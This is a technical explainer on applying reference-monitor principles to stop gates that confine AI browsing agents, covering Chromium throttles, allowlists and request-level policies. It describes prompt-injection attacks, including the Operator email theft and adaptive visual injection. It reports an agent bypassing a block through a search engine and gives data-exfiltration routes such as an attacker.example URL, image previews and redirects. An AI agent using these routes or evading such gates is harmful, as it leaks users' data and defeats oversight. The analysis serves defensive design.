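# The reference monitor principle applied to stop gates for AI browsing agents

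## Browsing agents, stop gates and the three requirements

A browsing agent is a program in which an AI model reads web pages and operates a browser by choosing what to click, what to type and which addresses to open. People use agents such as OpenAI's Atlas, Perplexity's Comet and Anthropic's Claude for Chrome to fill in forms, compare prices and place orders. A stop gate is a check that halts such an agent when a rule applies, either outright or until a person approves. For example, it might block every website except one, or pause the agent before a payment.

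Computer security has a standard for guards of this kind, called the reference monitor. The guard must always run, the guarded party must not be able to tamper with it, and it must be small enough for people to verify. The standard comes from James Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972), a report to the US Air Force on shared computers. Anderson worried about a user who is authorized to use the machine and writes hostile programs on it. A browsing agent poses a similar problem because it works inside the user's own browser, often with the user's accounts open, and text on a web page can turn it against the user.

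### One turn of a browsing agent

The agent works in a loop, which OpenAI's developer guide *Computer use* describes in five steps: send the task to the model, read the actions that the model returns, run them in order, send back a screenshot of the result, and repeat until the model returns no more actions. The model receives screenshots and produces requests. The harness, ordinary code that the developer controls, carries out each request in the browser.

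Suppose a user asks the agent to buy one coffee maker for under $50 at one shop. The harness captures the page of search results and sends it to the model, which replies with a request to click at x = 500, y = 300. In the version that Google's *Computer Use* guide describes, these coordinates refer to a 1000 by 1000 grid, so on a 1440 by 900 pixel screen the harness clicks at x = 720, y = 270. The click triggers whatever the page has attached to that spot, which may open a product page, add something to the cart or place an order. The harness waits for the page to settle, takes a new screenshot and starts the next turn.

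Requests from a browsing agent are hard for a gate to judge because they carry very little meaning. OpenAI's tool has nine of them (click, double-click, scroll, type, wait, keypress, drag, move and screenshot), and none of them is "buy". Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025), in *CELLMATE*, a design for confining browsing agents, point out that the same click can read an email or delete it, depending on what lies under the pointer. Security researchers call this problem the semantic gap. People write rules such as "do not place an order", but the gate receives events such as "click at these coordinates".

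The current OpenAI tool can return a batch of actions in one turn, so several clicks may happen between screenshots. A gate that runs once per turn would check only the first action. OpenAI also supports a harness in which the model writes short scripts and runs them against the browser. With this harness, the list of nine requests no longer limits what the model can do.

### The parts of a stop gate

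A stop gate has five parts. Interception is the point where the gate catches an event before it takes effect. The rule describes which events are acceptable. The verdict is the result of applying the rule to one event: allow, refuse or ask. The halt is whatever keeps the event from happening in the meantime. The human answer settles cases where the verdict is "ask".

For the coffee maker, the gate applies these rules:

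- The browser may contact the shop's own origins and the separate host that serves its product pictures, and nothing else. (An origin is the combination of protocol, host name and port by which browsers tell websites apart.)
- The gate stops the agent at any bank or sign-in page.
- Before an order goes out, the gate holds it and asks the user. The total must be under $50, and there may be only one order.

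The errand adapts examples from Meng and colleagues, who combine a $50 limit on an Amazon order with an allowlist, a list of permitted destinations, that includes Amazon's image host. The second rule is needed because the allowlist would block a bank's site but not the shop's own sign-in page, which is on a permitted origin. The limit of one order is needed because, as Meng and colleagues note, an agent can respect a $50 cap and still check out two carts at $49 each.

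Responsibility for the gate built into Google's tool is split between Google and the developer. An internal Google safety system applies Google's rule to each action the model proposes and can attach its verdict to the reply in a field called `safety_decision`. If the field requires confirmation, the developer's code must stop, ask the user, and run the action only if the user agrees, but nothing enforces this. The sample agent loop in Google's guide runs clicks without reading the field, although Google tells developers to check it in the surrounding text. A missing field also counts as permission, so if a bug drops the verdict before it reaches the harness, the click goes ahead.

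*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) defines the verdict formally. Its monitor has a state μ and answers every request with Allowed or Denied. After each step of the agent, with label ℓ, a function *mnext* μ ℓ computes the monitor's next state. The state lets a verdict depend on what has happened so far. For example, a monitor can withdraw a tool once the agent has read untrusted text or, in the shopping case, record that the agent has already sent an order.

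A gate that returns only Allowed or Denied can still ask a person, by holding the request until the person's answer determines which value to return. *Kairos* (2026), a monitor that can hold an agent's effects before releasing them, is based on the argument that whether an action is authorized often depends on what the user intended, which nobody can fully specify in advance. A monitor limited to yes and no, without the option to hold an action, must therefore err by either refusing legitimate work or releasing attacks. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) already used the word "prescript" for a rule that someone must follow before gaining access, so that human judgment has a chance to intervene.

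### Prompt injection and the hijacked agent

Prompt injection is text in a page or message that an AI model follows as if it were an instruction from its user. It works because the model receives the user's task and the page's content together and cannot reliably tell instructions from data. Meng and colleagues describe a real attack on Operator, an earlier OpenAI agent. The user asked it to look into an issue on GitHub, a site where programmers share code and report bugs. Anyone could post in that public project, and the attacker had written an issue telling the agent to open Hacker News, a forum where the user was logged in, copy the user's private email address and send it to the attacker's site. The attack relied on ambient authority, the power an agent has because of where it runs, and needed no bug in the browser. The agent could use the open Hacker News session even though the task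 had nothing to do with that site.

How often such attacks succeed depends heavily on how hard the attacker tries. Meng and colleagues reran WASP, a benchmark with fixed attack texts, and found success rates below 17% for OpenAI's o1 and below 7% for four other models. *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026) reports an average compromise rate above 90% on both kinds of agent interface when attackers adapt what the page displays. Pages that compromised one agent also compromised others. The two benchmarks differ in agents and set-up, so the numbers are not directly comparable. Still, a low attack success rate against fixed texts is a poor reason to trust an agent with one's accounts.

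Designers therefore judge a gate against a hijacked agent, assuming that an attacker makes its every choice. Honest mistakes are much easier to catch, because a mistaken agent isn't looking for a way around the check. If an agent overlooks the delivery charge and tries to buy a coffee maker for $54, almost any check on the ordinary path to the checkout will catch it. A hijacked agent will use whatever path the check leaves open. Saltzer and Schroeder insisted on this difference. They thought it wrong to claim that a system provided any security if it prevented mistakes but had no protection against a determined user, as was the case with many systems of their day. Anderson found the same fault in commercial operating systems, whose designers had assumed a friendly environment where violations happen only by accident.

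The hijacked-agent assumption also changes what counts as evidence. Saltzer and Schroeder observed that a flaw which opens an unwanted path stays invisible in normal use, because normal users do not try the path. A month of trouble-free shopping thus says very little about a gate. Anderson was nearly as hard on "tiger teams", groups of experts who try to break into a system. If the team gets in, it has found a flaw. If it fails, the system's security is simply unknown. (No known team had failed at the time.)

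In return, nobody has to predict what the model will do. The main theorem in *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) holds even for an agent that is prompt-injected, backdoored or deliberately breaking its contract. It assumes that the monitor is correct, that the attacker has not compromised it, and that every relevant effect reaches it before execution. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) also makes its assumptions about the monitor rather than the agent. Its attacker can influence the agent and knows the tools and the security policy, but cannot bypass the monitor, disable it or rewrite the policy. Whoever builds a stop gate for a browser has to build in these properties rather than assume them.

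Testing a gate under this assumption doesn't require a working injection. Meng and colleagues wrote browser scripts for 12 attacker goals on GitLab, a site for hosting code, including deleting projects and adding the attacker's own login key. Each script pursued its goal directly, as a fully hijacked agent would, and CELLMATE blocked all 12. Every goal required an action that the active policy forbade, so the test covers enforcement but not what an attacker can do with permitted actions. An agent with permission to comment can post a harmful comment, and a hijacked shopping agent can pick a terrible coffee maker for $49, which the user might approve.

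### Anderson's three requirements

The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to work on one computer at the same time. Anderson's panel proposed checking every reference a program makes to data, a device or another program against a list of authorized kinds of reference. One can picture the list as a table with a row for each subject (a user or program), a column for each object (such as a file) and the permitted operations in the cells. For a stop gate, the subject is the agent, the objects are pages and accounts, and the operations include reading a page and submitting an order.

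The report set three requirements for the mechanism that does the checking:

- It must be tamper proof. Anderson considered this one obvious, since a guard that an attacker can alter protects nothing. The modern term is tamper resistance.
- It must always be invoked. If some programs can skip the check, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must meet the other two requirements themselves. This is complete mediation.
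- It must be small enough for analysis and tests whose completeness someone can assure. Otherwise nobody can know that the first two requirements hold, and there is no basis for certifying the system. This is verifiability.

Anderson's example of failure shows how the requirements interact. On the HIS 635, a Honeywell mainframe, a hardware register kept each user's program inside its own area of memory. But to read or write a file, the program had to call the operating system, GCOS III, which acted on the user's behalf and mostly ran with the memory check switched off, so the check did not always run. Treating GCOS III itself as the guard would have meant a guard of 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many for complete analysis, and attackers had already broken into it several times. Someone who puts a stop gate in a browser and counts the whole browser as part of the guard has the same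 problem, with a much larger program.

Saltzer and Schroeder gave complete mediation its usual wording: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They concluded that the check must cover startup, recovery, shutdown and maintenance as well as normal operation, which for a browser includes the moments just after a restart. They also required a foolproof way to identify the source of each request, so a stop gate must be able to tell the agent's click from the user's. They added that designers should be suspicious of any scheme that remembers an earlier verdict to save time. For example, if the user approves a cart at $42 and the agent then adds a second item, the old approval must lapse. Finally, they called for "economy of mechanism", a design as simple and small as possible, because finding hidden access paths takes line-by-line inspection.

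The current official wording is in control AC-25 of *Security and Privacy Controls for Information Systems and Organizations*, the 2020 catalogue of safeguards from NIST, the US standards institute. AC-25 calls for a reference monitor that is "tamperproof, always invoked, and small enough to be subject to analysis and testing", and it keeps Anderson's condition that the completeness of that analysis can be assured. The explanation beneath the control refers to "determined adversaries", so NIST, like Anderson, has deliberate attack in mind. NIST did not revise AC-25 when it updated the catalogue in August 2025.

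These requirements exclude one popular kind of gate. OpenAI's guide offers paragraphs for developers to paste into the agent's instructions, telling the model to stop and ask when a page looks like an attack. Such instructions may well reduce accidents, but *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), a study of AI agents as operating systems, argues that they cannot be a reference monitor, because they reach the model in the same input as the hostile text, which can override them. The check must be outside the model and must also cover every path. If a second model does the checking, it reads text that the agent controls.

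Outside the browser, designers can meet the requirements fairly directly. *Causality Laundering* (2026) presents ARM, a gate for agents that call named tools instead of clicking on pages. ARM is the only connection between the model's client and the tool server, which gives it complete mediation. It runs in a separate process from the model, so the agent cannot change its rules. Its four layers are deterministic, and an engineer can test each one alone. Complete mediation depends on a deployment in which the agent has no other path to the tools, whereas a browser offers many other paths because it is designed to reach other places.

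### The monitor, the mechanism and the trusted computing base

Anderson's report distinguishes the reference monitor, the abstract rule that every reference goes through a check, from the reference validation mechanism, the hardware and software that does the checking in a particular system. The report calls the software part of this mechanism the "security kernel". The trusted computing base is a broader term that covers all the hardware and software whose failure could break the rule.

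In CELLMATE, the abstract idea is that every web request from the agent's session goes through a policy, and the mechanism is a Chrome extension that intercepts those requests. The trusted computing base contains the extension, Chrome, the operating system, any other extension able to interfere with network requests, the policies, and a list from the website that identifies which request places an order. If the website's list is wrong about that request, the order can still go out even when the extension works as designed. Meng and colleagues accept this, and where the list is incomplete or incorrect, the user has only the protection that existed before CELLMATE.

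Moving the gate changes what people have to trust. *Architectures for Inlining Security Monitors in Web Applications*, by Magazinius, Hedin and Sabelfeld, compares several positions for a monitor that controls the scripts on web pages. As a browser extension, the monitor had strong integrity and complete mediation, but it ran with the browser's privileges, so a faulty monitor could endanger the entire browser. As a proxy, a server that relays the traffic, it didn't need those privileges, but it could read everything the user sent and received, including encrypted pages, so it became part of the trusted computing base.

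Magazinius and colleagues add that Anderson's principles make it easier to establish that a monitor enforces the right policy, but do not guarantee that it does. If the user meant a $50 limit to include delivery but the rule checks only the item price, a gate that meets all three requirements will enforce the wrong limit every time.

### Which mechanism serves which requirement

Most of the mechanisms available to a gate's designer contribute mainly to one requirement, though not always the one their names suggest. Isolation protects the gate from tampering, but it also helps make mediation complete. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) argues that mediation is complete only if the agent has no other way to act, and isolation removes the other ways. Separate credentials also help make mediation complete. In *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026), a design for agents that manage cloud systems, every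 path that can change something rejects any credential except the broker's, so an agent that gets around the broker has no credential those paths will accept.

| Mechanism | Requirement | Effect on the coffee-maker errand |
|---|---|---|
| Covering every route to a page | Complete mediation | The agent cannot reach a bank page by a route that skips the gate |
| Checking web requests instead of clicks | Complete mediation | The gate sees the order whichever button or script sends it |
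| Running the gate in a separate process | Tamper resistance, and complete mediation where isolation closes other channels | The agent cannot edit the list of permitted hosts or the $50 limit |
| Halting the browser and asking the user | Complete mediation for the halt, tamper resistance for the approval | The order waits for an answer, and the agent cannot supply that answer itself |
| Separate credentials | Complete mediation | An order that avoids the gate lacks the credential to go through |
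| Enforcement at the network | Complete mediation, and tamper resistance if the enforcer sits on another machine | Connections to other hosts fail even if the attacker controls the browser |
| A small gate, with formal verification where possible | Verifiability | A reviewer can check all the code that decides whether an order goes out |

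## Catching every route to a page

A browser can contact a website when an agent enters an address or clicks a link, when a page loads a picture from another host, or when a script opens a connection in the background. Complete mediation requires a stop gate to check all of these routes. A gate on the agent's "navigate" command, the most obvious place for one, checks only the addresses the agent enters.

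### The routes

Browsers contact servers both when they navigate and when they load a page. *Life of a Navigation*, from the documentation for Chromium, the open-source browser on which Google builds Chrome, uses "navigation" for the phase when the browser requests a document and commits to showing it. In the loading phase that follows, the browser runs the page's scripts and fetches the pictures and other files that the page refers to.

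A navigation can start from the address bar, a link, a form or a script, and its destination can change on the way. In a server redirect, the server answers a request with a different address, which the browser requests before any new page appears. In a client redirect, a page opens and its code then sends the browser to another address. Chromium's *Navigation Concepts* treats a server redirect as part of the original navigation and a client redirect as the start of a new one.

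Background requests are far more varied. Franken, Van Goethem and Joosen (2018), in *Who Left Open the Cookie Jar?*, tested browsers and extensions that claim to block requests to advertisers and trackers, so they needed a list of everything that can trigger a request. HTML, the language of web pages, alone accounted for 196 methods. They found more in response headers, JavaScript and scripts inside PDF files. Their list also includes service workers and WebSockets. A service worker is a script that a site installs in the browser, where it handles the site's later requests and can make its own. A WebSocket is a connection that stays open so the page and a server can exchange messages at any time.

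Suppose the gate for the coffee-maker errand consults its allowlist only when the agent issues a "navigate" command. It then catches one route out of twelve:

| Route | Example on the coffee-maker errand | Caught? |
|---|---|---|
| Typed address | The agent asks the browser to open a bank's address | Yes |
| Link | The agent clicks a link in a product review | No |
| Form | The agent submits a form that sends its contents to another host | No |
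| Server redirect | An address at the shop answers with the address of an outside site | No, the gate sees only the first address |
| Script | A page's code sends the tab to another site | No |
| New tab | A click opens an advertiser's site in a second tab | No |
| Back button | The agent returns to a bank page that the user visited earlier | No |
| Embedded frame | The product page displays part of another site | No |
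| Background request | The page fetches a picture from an address that contains the user's email | No |
| Service worker | A script that the shop installed last month makes a request | No |
| WebSocket | A chat window holds open a connection to another company | No |
| Another tool | The agent runs a script or a download command | No |

A hijacked agent can't use all of these routes at will. Most background requests come from a page's own code, and an attacker who writes a product review usually controls only text. This is the best argument for a gate that checks only navigations, because if the agent never leaves the shop's site, only code the shop has chosen will run.

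The argument fails if a permitted site displays material from other hosts. Suppose the shop's review form accepts pictures from any site. A hijacked agent can write a review that includes a picture on the attacker's site, with the user's email address in the picture's URL. When the browser previews the review, it requests the picture and sends the email address to the attacker, even though the tab never left the shop's site.

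### Complete mediation as set inclusion

Let R be the set of routes by which anything in the agent's session can contact a site. Let C be the set of routes on which the gate reaches its verdict before the contact happens. Complete mediation is then the condition

R ⊆ C

which means that every possible route is also a checked route. In the coffee-maker example, R has at least twelve members and C has one. A single route in R that is missing from C breaks the condition.

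A designer can work on either set. Removing features from the browser or tools from the agent makes R smaller. Playwright MCP, for example, lets AI models operate a browser through the Playwright automation library, and its *Configuration* guide lists an option that blocks service workers. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a common standard for connecting models to tools.) Google's Chrome for Developers site describes a similar product, Chrome DevTools for agents, which gives models access to Chrome's debugging tools. Users can switch off script execution, which is on by default. Doing so also blocks navigation to `javascript:` addresses, which run code instead of opening a page.

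Meng and colleagues make R smaller by assuming, in their threat model for CELLMATE, that the agent can click, type and navigate within web pages but cannot change browser settings, open local files or use developer tools. They suggest that companies can enforce these limits through Chrome's administrator policies. An agent that also has a command line on the user's computer falls outside the model, since it can download a page without using the browser.

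Making C larger one route at a time is difficult because nobody has a complete list of R. Franken and colleagues found no comprehensive list of the features that can start a request, so they assembled their own from the test suites of browser engines and checked it against several specifications. Browser makers also keep adding features, so a gate that covered every route last year may miss some now. The more promising approach is to put the gate at a point that all requests have to pass, whatever started them.

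### The search-engine detour

In a preliminary experiment, Meng and colleagues saw the failure of a gate that covered only one route to a page. They used Browser Use, an open-source library for building browsing agents, and blocked the agent from navigating directly to Hacker News, the forum in the Operator attack. The agent searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

The paper describes the agent as finding this detour autonomously. This is worse for the gate than a successful attack, because it means a check on one command can fail even against an agent that is only trying to finish its task. The experiment is an illustration and has no reported success rate, but that hardly matters for complete mediation, since one example is enough to show that R is not inside C.

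Meng and colleagues conclude that nobody can list and block every sequence of actions that leads to a given page. That seems right for clicks and keystrokes. But each of those sequences ends with the browser requesting a page from Hacker News, so a gate that checked the destination of every navigation would have stopped this detour without predicting it.

### Browser Use's watchdog

Browser Use does more than check the "navigate" command. Browser Use's *Safety* guide offers developers a list of allowed domains to restrict where an agent can go, and a component called the security watchdog enforces such a list inside the library. In a fork of the project (a copy that other developers maintain), the watchdog in Browser Use reacts to three events:

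- `NavigateToUrlEvent`, an explicit command to open an address. The watchdog compares the address with the list before the navigation starts. If the address is not allowed, it raises an error, which stops the navigation.
- `NavigationCompleteEvent`, which comes once a navigation has finished. The watchdog checks the address where the browser ended up, "in case of redirects" as a comment in the code puts it, and closes the tab if that address is not allowed.
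- `TabCreatedEvent`, which comes once a new tab exists. The watchdog checks the tab's address and tries to close the tab if necessary.

The check before navigation runs in time, though it has had errors, including one in how it read addresses, which OSV, a database of software vulnerabilities, rates as critical. The other two checks run too late. Suppose the shop has an address that forwards visitors to its advertisers, and a hijacked agent opens that address with the attacker's site as the destination. The watchdog checks the shop's host name and lets the navigation start. The shop's server answers with a redirect, the browser follows it, and the attacker's server receives a request and sends back a page. The watchdog compares the attacker's address with the list and closes the tab only after all this has happened.

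The watchdog can check an ordinary link only after the navigation completes, because none of its three events is a click. It has no event for pictures, background requests or WebSockets.

The watchdog also fails open in two situations. If closing a tab produces an error, the code logs the failure and continues, leaving the forbidden page open. And if the developer has set no allowed domains, the watchdog allows every address. That default is reasonable for a general-purpose library, but a configuration mistake that empties the list removes the gate without warning.

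### Why a late check cannot recall data

A request carries data to the server before any page comes back, and the simplest place to put that data is the URL. If a hijacked agent opens `https://attacker.example/?email=alice@mail.example`, the attacker's server can read Alice's email address from the request, even if it never returns a page. Closing the tab afterwards doesn't delete the server's copy.

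A redirect can pass on much more data when the agent submits a form. The browser usually follows a redirect with a request that has no body, but according to Chromium, response codes 307 and 308 make it repeat the original method and body. If the agent submits a delivery form to a URL that responds with either code, the next server also receives the user's name, street and telephone number.

Requests can also change data on a site. Browsers commonly attach cookies, the small pieces of data that keep a user logged in, so the receiving site may treat a request as the user's own. Careful sites do not let a plain page request change anything, but Franken and colleagues describe this as best practice, so some sites may not follow it. If a single request can cancel an order, a gate that checks the address after the page loads is too late to prevent the cancellation.

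Late checks are still useful against accidents. If an honest agent follows an advertisement to the wrong shop, closing the tab prevents it from buying the coffee maker there. A late check can stop the agent's next step, but it cannot keep information from leaving, and the Operator attack aimed to extract information. Someone who reviews a log of addresses at the end of the day has the same limitation, with a longer delay.

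### Chromium's checks during a navigation

Chromium has hooks that allow a gate to act earlier. A navigation throttle is browser code that can delay, block or cancel a navigation in progress. Chromium (2025) defines one for AI agents, `ActorNavigationThrottle`, which applies safety policies in tabs controlled by the "actor", Chromium's term for the agent. A check on "navigate" misses the case where the agent clicks a link to a blocked site, but the throttle intercepts that navigation, according to a comment in the code.

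The throttle has three hooks. `WillStartRequest` runs before the browser sends the request, `WillRedirectRequest` runs at every server redirect, and `WillProcessResponse` runs when the response's headers have arrived but the page has not opened. They differ in what they can still prevent:

| When the check runs | What has already gone out | What the gate can still prevent |
|---|---|---|
| `WillStartRequest` | Nothing from this navigation | Any contact with the destination |
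| `WillRedirectRequest` | The request to the server that answered with the redirect | Contact with the next server |
| `WillProcessResponse` | The full request to the destination | The page opening in the tab |
| After loading, as in Browser Use's watchdog | The full request and anything the page's scripts have sent | The agent's next action on the page |

In the example of the shop's forwarding address, the check at the start would pass because the address belongs to the shop. The check at the redirect would then run on the attacker's address, before the browser contacted the attacker's server. `ActorNavigationThrottle` declares one function for both checks, with a flag that marks redirects, so an address can go through the same policy check whether or not the browser was redirected to it.

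The hooks can also halt a navigation. A throttle can defer a navigation, which then waits until the throttle resumes or cancels it, according to comments in the general throttle code (Chromium, 2015). If the browser discards the navigation in the meantime, for instance because the tab closes, the request is cancelled too. A gate can therefore hold a navigation while it looks up a policy or waits for a person. A later version of the agent's throttle (Chromium, 2025) adds a function that receives a "navigation confirmation decision", and Chromium's policy code allows either blocking an address or asking the user to confirm it.

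The drawback of checking early is that the address may not be final. Many sites still contain unencrypted `http://` links, which the browser then upgrades to `https://`. Chromium's policy check has a setting that allows these addresses, because refusing them before the upgrade would obstruct the agent too often. This leniency is tolerable because the gate checks the address again at each redirect.

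### Navigations that skip the throttles

Some navigations never reach a throttle, most clearly when the browser displays a page it already has in memory. In Chromium, this happens when the browser activates a prerendered page, which it loaded in advance because the user seemed likely to open it, or restores a page from the back-forward cache, which keeps recently visited pages ready for the Back and Forward buttons.

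Suppose the user read a bank statement and then handed the same tab to the agent for the errand. If the agent uses the Back button, Chromium can restore the bank page from memory without making a request or running any throttle. Nothing reaches an outside website at that moment, but the agent's next screenshot may send the statement to the model. The throttle alone cannot catch the restored page, but Chromium also checks whether the agent may act on a given tab, and that check could catch the page at that stage.

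Prerendering is a smaller problem. A separate throttle in Chromium cancels prerendering if the page comes from a different origin or redirects to one, so a shop's page normally cannot prerender a bank's page.

Same-document navigations are another exception. These change the address while the same document stays open, as when a link leads to a heading further down the page. Throttles can register for an extra hook, `WillCommitWithoutUrlLoader`, which covers some of these navigations but not those in which a page's own script changes the address. According to comments in Chromium's code, the process that runs the page makes that change itself and notifies the main browser process only afterwards.

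A script can change the address in this way only within the page's own origin, so an allowlist of origins still works. But the coffee-maker errand also has a rule that stops the agent at sign-in pages, and that rule can fail. Many shops are built as a single document that swaps its contents as the user moves around. On such a site, the agent can get from the coffee maker to the sign-in form without a navigation that any throttle could stop. To catch this, the gate would have to inspect the page's contents or the requests behind it.

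The largest omission in Chromium's design is background requests. A throttle handles only navigations, so it misses what happens after a navigation has committed, when the browser fetches pictures, runs scripts and opens WebSockets. The design covers links, forms and redirects far better than Browser Use's watchdog does, but it would not stop the browser from fetching the preview picture in the review form.

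### Filters that cover background requests

Several tools for browsing agents filter more than navigations, although their coverage varies a lot. Playwright MCP accepts a list of origins the browser may request and a list of origins to block, and it checks the blocklist first. Its developers write in Playwright's guide that the lists are "not a security boundary", because they do not affect redirects and someone can deliberately work around them. The developers present the lists as a convenience for catching unintended access. For real isolation, they recommend permissions in the client, the program that connects the model to its tools.

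The origin lists might well catch an agent that misreads a link, but the shop's forwarding address would bypass them. Playwright's *Networking and Security* page tells people never to browse untrusted content with Playwright, because a web page could escape the browser and run code on the user's machine. A shopping agent has to read reviews written by strangers, so by that standard Playwright alone is unsuitable for the errand.

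Chrome DevTools for agents has a broader filter. Google declared the tool stable in June 2026, according to Chrome for Developers' *What's new in DevTools (Chrome 149)* (2026). The filter's `blockedUrlPattern` option blocks both navigations and subresources (the pictures, scripts and other files that a page loads), while `allowedUrlPattern` permits only addresses that match a pattern. The errand needs `allowedUrlPattern`, because a blocklist would have to name every site an attacker might use. With background requests under the same filter, the browser would refuse to fetch the preview picture from the attacker's site.

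The allowlist requires Chrome 149 or later. Classmethod's *I tried to use the Chrome DevTools MCP URL allowlist* (2026) describes a test with Kitesurf, a browser for AI agents that runs on Cloudflare's servers and reports itself as Chrome 145. The connection succeeded, but the first operation on a page failed with an error about the required version. This is the right way to fail, since the tool did not run without its filter. When the tester removed the allowlist as a diagnostic, everything worked.

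The tester confirmed from the log that the agent visited no forbidden address during that second run. Classmethod's article still advises against relying on such a log for production systems or administration pages, because an audit cannot stop a communication that has already happened. The episode also shows that a gate can disappear without an attacker, since someone who finds that the filter keeps the agent from working has a strong reason to delete one line from the configuration.

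The allowlists in two other products give quite different protection. Browserbase, which rents out browsers for automated use, has an experimental list of allowed domains that checks only top-level navigations, which change the main page in a tab. It doesn't check embedded frames or background requests, and allowing a domain also allows all of its subdomains. The list in agent-browser, a command-line tool for agents, covers navigations, subresources, WebSockets and two other kinds of background connection.

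### What happened to earlier request blockers

Ad blockers had to catch every request to certain hosts years before browsing agents existed, and their opponents have money at stake. Franken and colleagues tested 7 browsers, 31 ad-blocking extensions and 15 anti-tracking extensions. Their program generated a page for each way of triggering a request, opened it in each browser, and used a proxy to record what the browser sent. Every built-in protection and every extension missed at least one route.

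The reasons are instructive for anyone who builds a stop gate:

- Many extensions asked the browser to report requests whose addresses began with `http://` or `https://`. WebSocket addresses begin with `ws://` or `wss://`, so the extensions never heard about them.
- In Chrome and Opera, no extension could stop requests from scripts inside PDF files. The PDF viewer was itself an extension, and browsers did not let one extension intercept the traffic of another.
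- In Firefox, a bug kept the browser from reporting requests for a certain kind of site icon.
- Firefox's own tracking protection had one central check, but the check ran only if the feature making the request had set a flag. The developers had added the protection to an existing browser and would have had to change every such feature. In the HTML tests it blocked 46 of 51 requests.

Another failure especially relevant to agents involved requests from service workers and from an older feature called AppCache. In Chrome, these requests did reach the extensions, but with a tab number of −1 instead of a real one. Chrome also used −1 for some of its own functions, such as completing addresses as the user types, so most extensions ignored requests with that number to avoid breaking something. As a result, 26 extensions let AppCache requests through and 20 let service-worker requests through. Firefox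 labelled service-worker requests with the tab that had installed the worker, and the extensions blocked them there.

A stop gate often has to tell the agent's requests from the user's, because the two may share one browser and the rules apply only to the agent. The natural way is to check which tab a request came from, but a service worker serves a whole site and may act for several tabs at once, so its requests may not belong to any one tab. If the gate ignores requests that have no tab, a hijacked agent can use them to reach a page, but blocking them all may interfere with the user's own browsing. Giving the agent a separate browser avoids this choice, because the gate can then apply the rules to every request from that browser.

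Franken and colleagues also looked for routes missing from their list. They visited about 160,000 pages on popular sites and compared the requests they had captured with the browser's DNS lookups, in which it asks for the network address of a host name. After they allowed more time for slow pages, 865 pages still produced lookups without a matching request. Most came from prefetching, where the browser looks up a name in case the user follows a link. They found no new way around the blockers. But a stop gate that checks only page requests would miss these lookups, and a lookup is itself a small leak, because an attacker who runs a domain's name server can read whatever is in the host name.

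Their crawl found no tracker deliberately using the new bypasses. This is only slightly reassuring, because Pornhub had earlier used WebSockets to get its advertisements past ad blockers. Browser makers did not let extensions intercept WebSockets until years after introducing them.

Some of these holes have closed since 2018. Chrome and Firefox have removed AppCache, for example. Google also scheduled a more general mechanism, Connection Allowlists, for trial use in Chrome 148 to 151, as daily.dev reports. A website sends the browser a list of permitted addresses along with a page, and the browser refuses all other connections from that page, including background requests, redirects and WebSockets. Refusing by default suits complete mediation better than a list of known routes does, because a request needs permission whichever feature started it. Because the website supplies the list, the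 shop could use it to confine its own pages, but a user who wants to confine an agent would still need a gate that applies to every site.

CELLMATE is an attempt at such a gate. Meng and colleagues claim it achieves complete mediation because it checks web requests, regardless of which click produced them. Since CELLMATE is a Chrome extension, that claim depends on Chrome letting extensions see every request. In 2018, Chrome did not let them see requests made by scripts in PDFs.

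## Checking web requests instead of clicks

A gate that intercepts every web request must still identify the few that matter. Opening one product page can trigger dozens of requests for pictures and scripts, but only one request in the whole shopping task places the order. CELLMATE relies on the fact that a web request, unlike a click, usually identifies the operation it carries out.

### The semantic gap

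Meng and colleagues show why rules about clicks fail by imagining a policy that allows the agent to click only at (246, 1023). The policy is useless because those coordinates mean something different on every website. Even on one site, their meaning depends on the screen resolution and what the page is showing.

Other systems have a milder form of this problem. A Linux program has to request a file from the operating system by name, so an administrator can write a rule about that file. A browsing agent's clicks and keystrokes contain nothing comparable that a rule could refer to.

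A gate could try to close the gap by reading the page, for instance by looking up the label of the button under the pointer before each click. Two known attacks make this unreliable. In a time-of-check to time-of-use attack, the page changes after the gate has looked but before the click takes effect. A 2025 security advisory that Meng and colleagues cite describes using this attack to make OpenAI's Operator click on a site of the attacker's choice. In branch steering, an attacker manipulates buttons or other elements so that the agent triggers a valid action it did not intend.

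The request that follows a click is easier to judge than the click itself. Browsers communicate with websites through HTTP requests, each of which has a method (usually GET to fetch data or POST to submit it), an address and sometimes a body with further data. To add a login key to a GitLab account, the browser sends a POST request to `/-/user_settings/ssh_keys` on gitlab.com. GitLab's server adds the key only when it receives that request, whether the agent clicked a button or pressed Enter. GitLab can redesign the settings page without changing the request, and an attacker who can only post comments cannot change it.

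### A map from requests to actions

The gate still has to know which request does what. CELLMATE gets this information from an "agent sitemap", a file that the website publishes at a standard address. Part of the example for Amazon looks like this, with an asterisk standing for any text:

| Method | Address on www.amazon.com | Named action |
|---|---|---|
| GET | `/gp/cart/view.html*` | ViewCart |
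| POST | `/cart*` | UpdateCart |
| POST | `/checkout/p/*/spc/place-order*` | PlaceOrder |

An entry can also match on the body of a request, which helps when a site sends many operations to one address. It can also list arguments, such as an order's total, and where to find them.

Each policy then allows one or more of the named actions, denies them or allows them under a condition. The Amazon policy `view_shopping_cart` allows ViewCart, and `purchase_amount_leq` allows PlaceOrder if the total is within a limit. Meng and colleagues expect these policies to come from the website's developers, company administrators or trusted outsiders, such as the maintainers of the ad-blocking list EasyList.

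### From the user's task to a policy

Suppose the user types "Buy one coffee maker on Amazon for under $50". CELLMATE turns the request into permissions before the agent starts:

1. A language model reads the task and lists the sites that the agent needs, in this case amazon.com.
2. For each site, the model reads the task again together with the site's prewritten policies. It picks the smallest set that is enough for the task and fills in any values, such as a maximum of $50.
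3. CELLMATE merges the chosen policies and adds other hosts that the site's developers trust, such as the one that serves Amazon's pictures.
4. A dialog shows the user the policies, their descriptions and the values. The user can change any of them.
5. Once the user confirms, the policy stays fixed for the agent's browser session unless the user updates it.

The model that picks the permissions never reads a web page, so an attacker cannot use a product review to make it grant more. This is the main advantage over letting the agent request permissions while it browses.

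Picking the smallest set makes sense only if the policies are comparable. Let A(p) be the set of actions that policy p allows. If A(p) ⊂ A(q) and both are enough for the task, p is the better choice because it allows less. If p and q each allow something that the other forbids, neither is smaller and "least privilege" has no clear meaning. Meng and colleagues therefore require a site's policies to form a partial order under set inclusion, so the least-privileged choice is clear whenever several policies cover the same actions.

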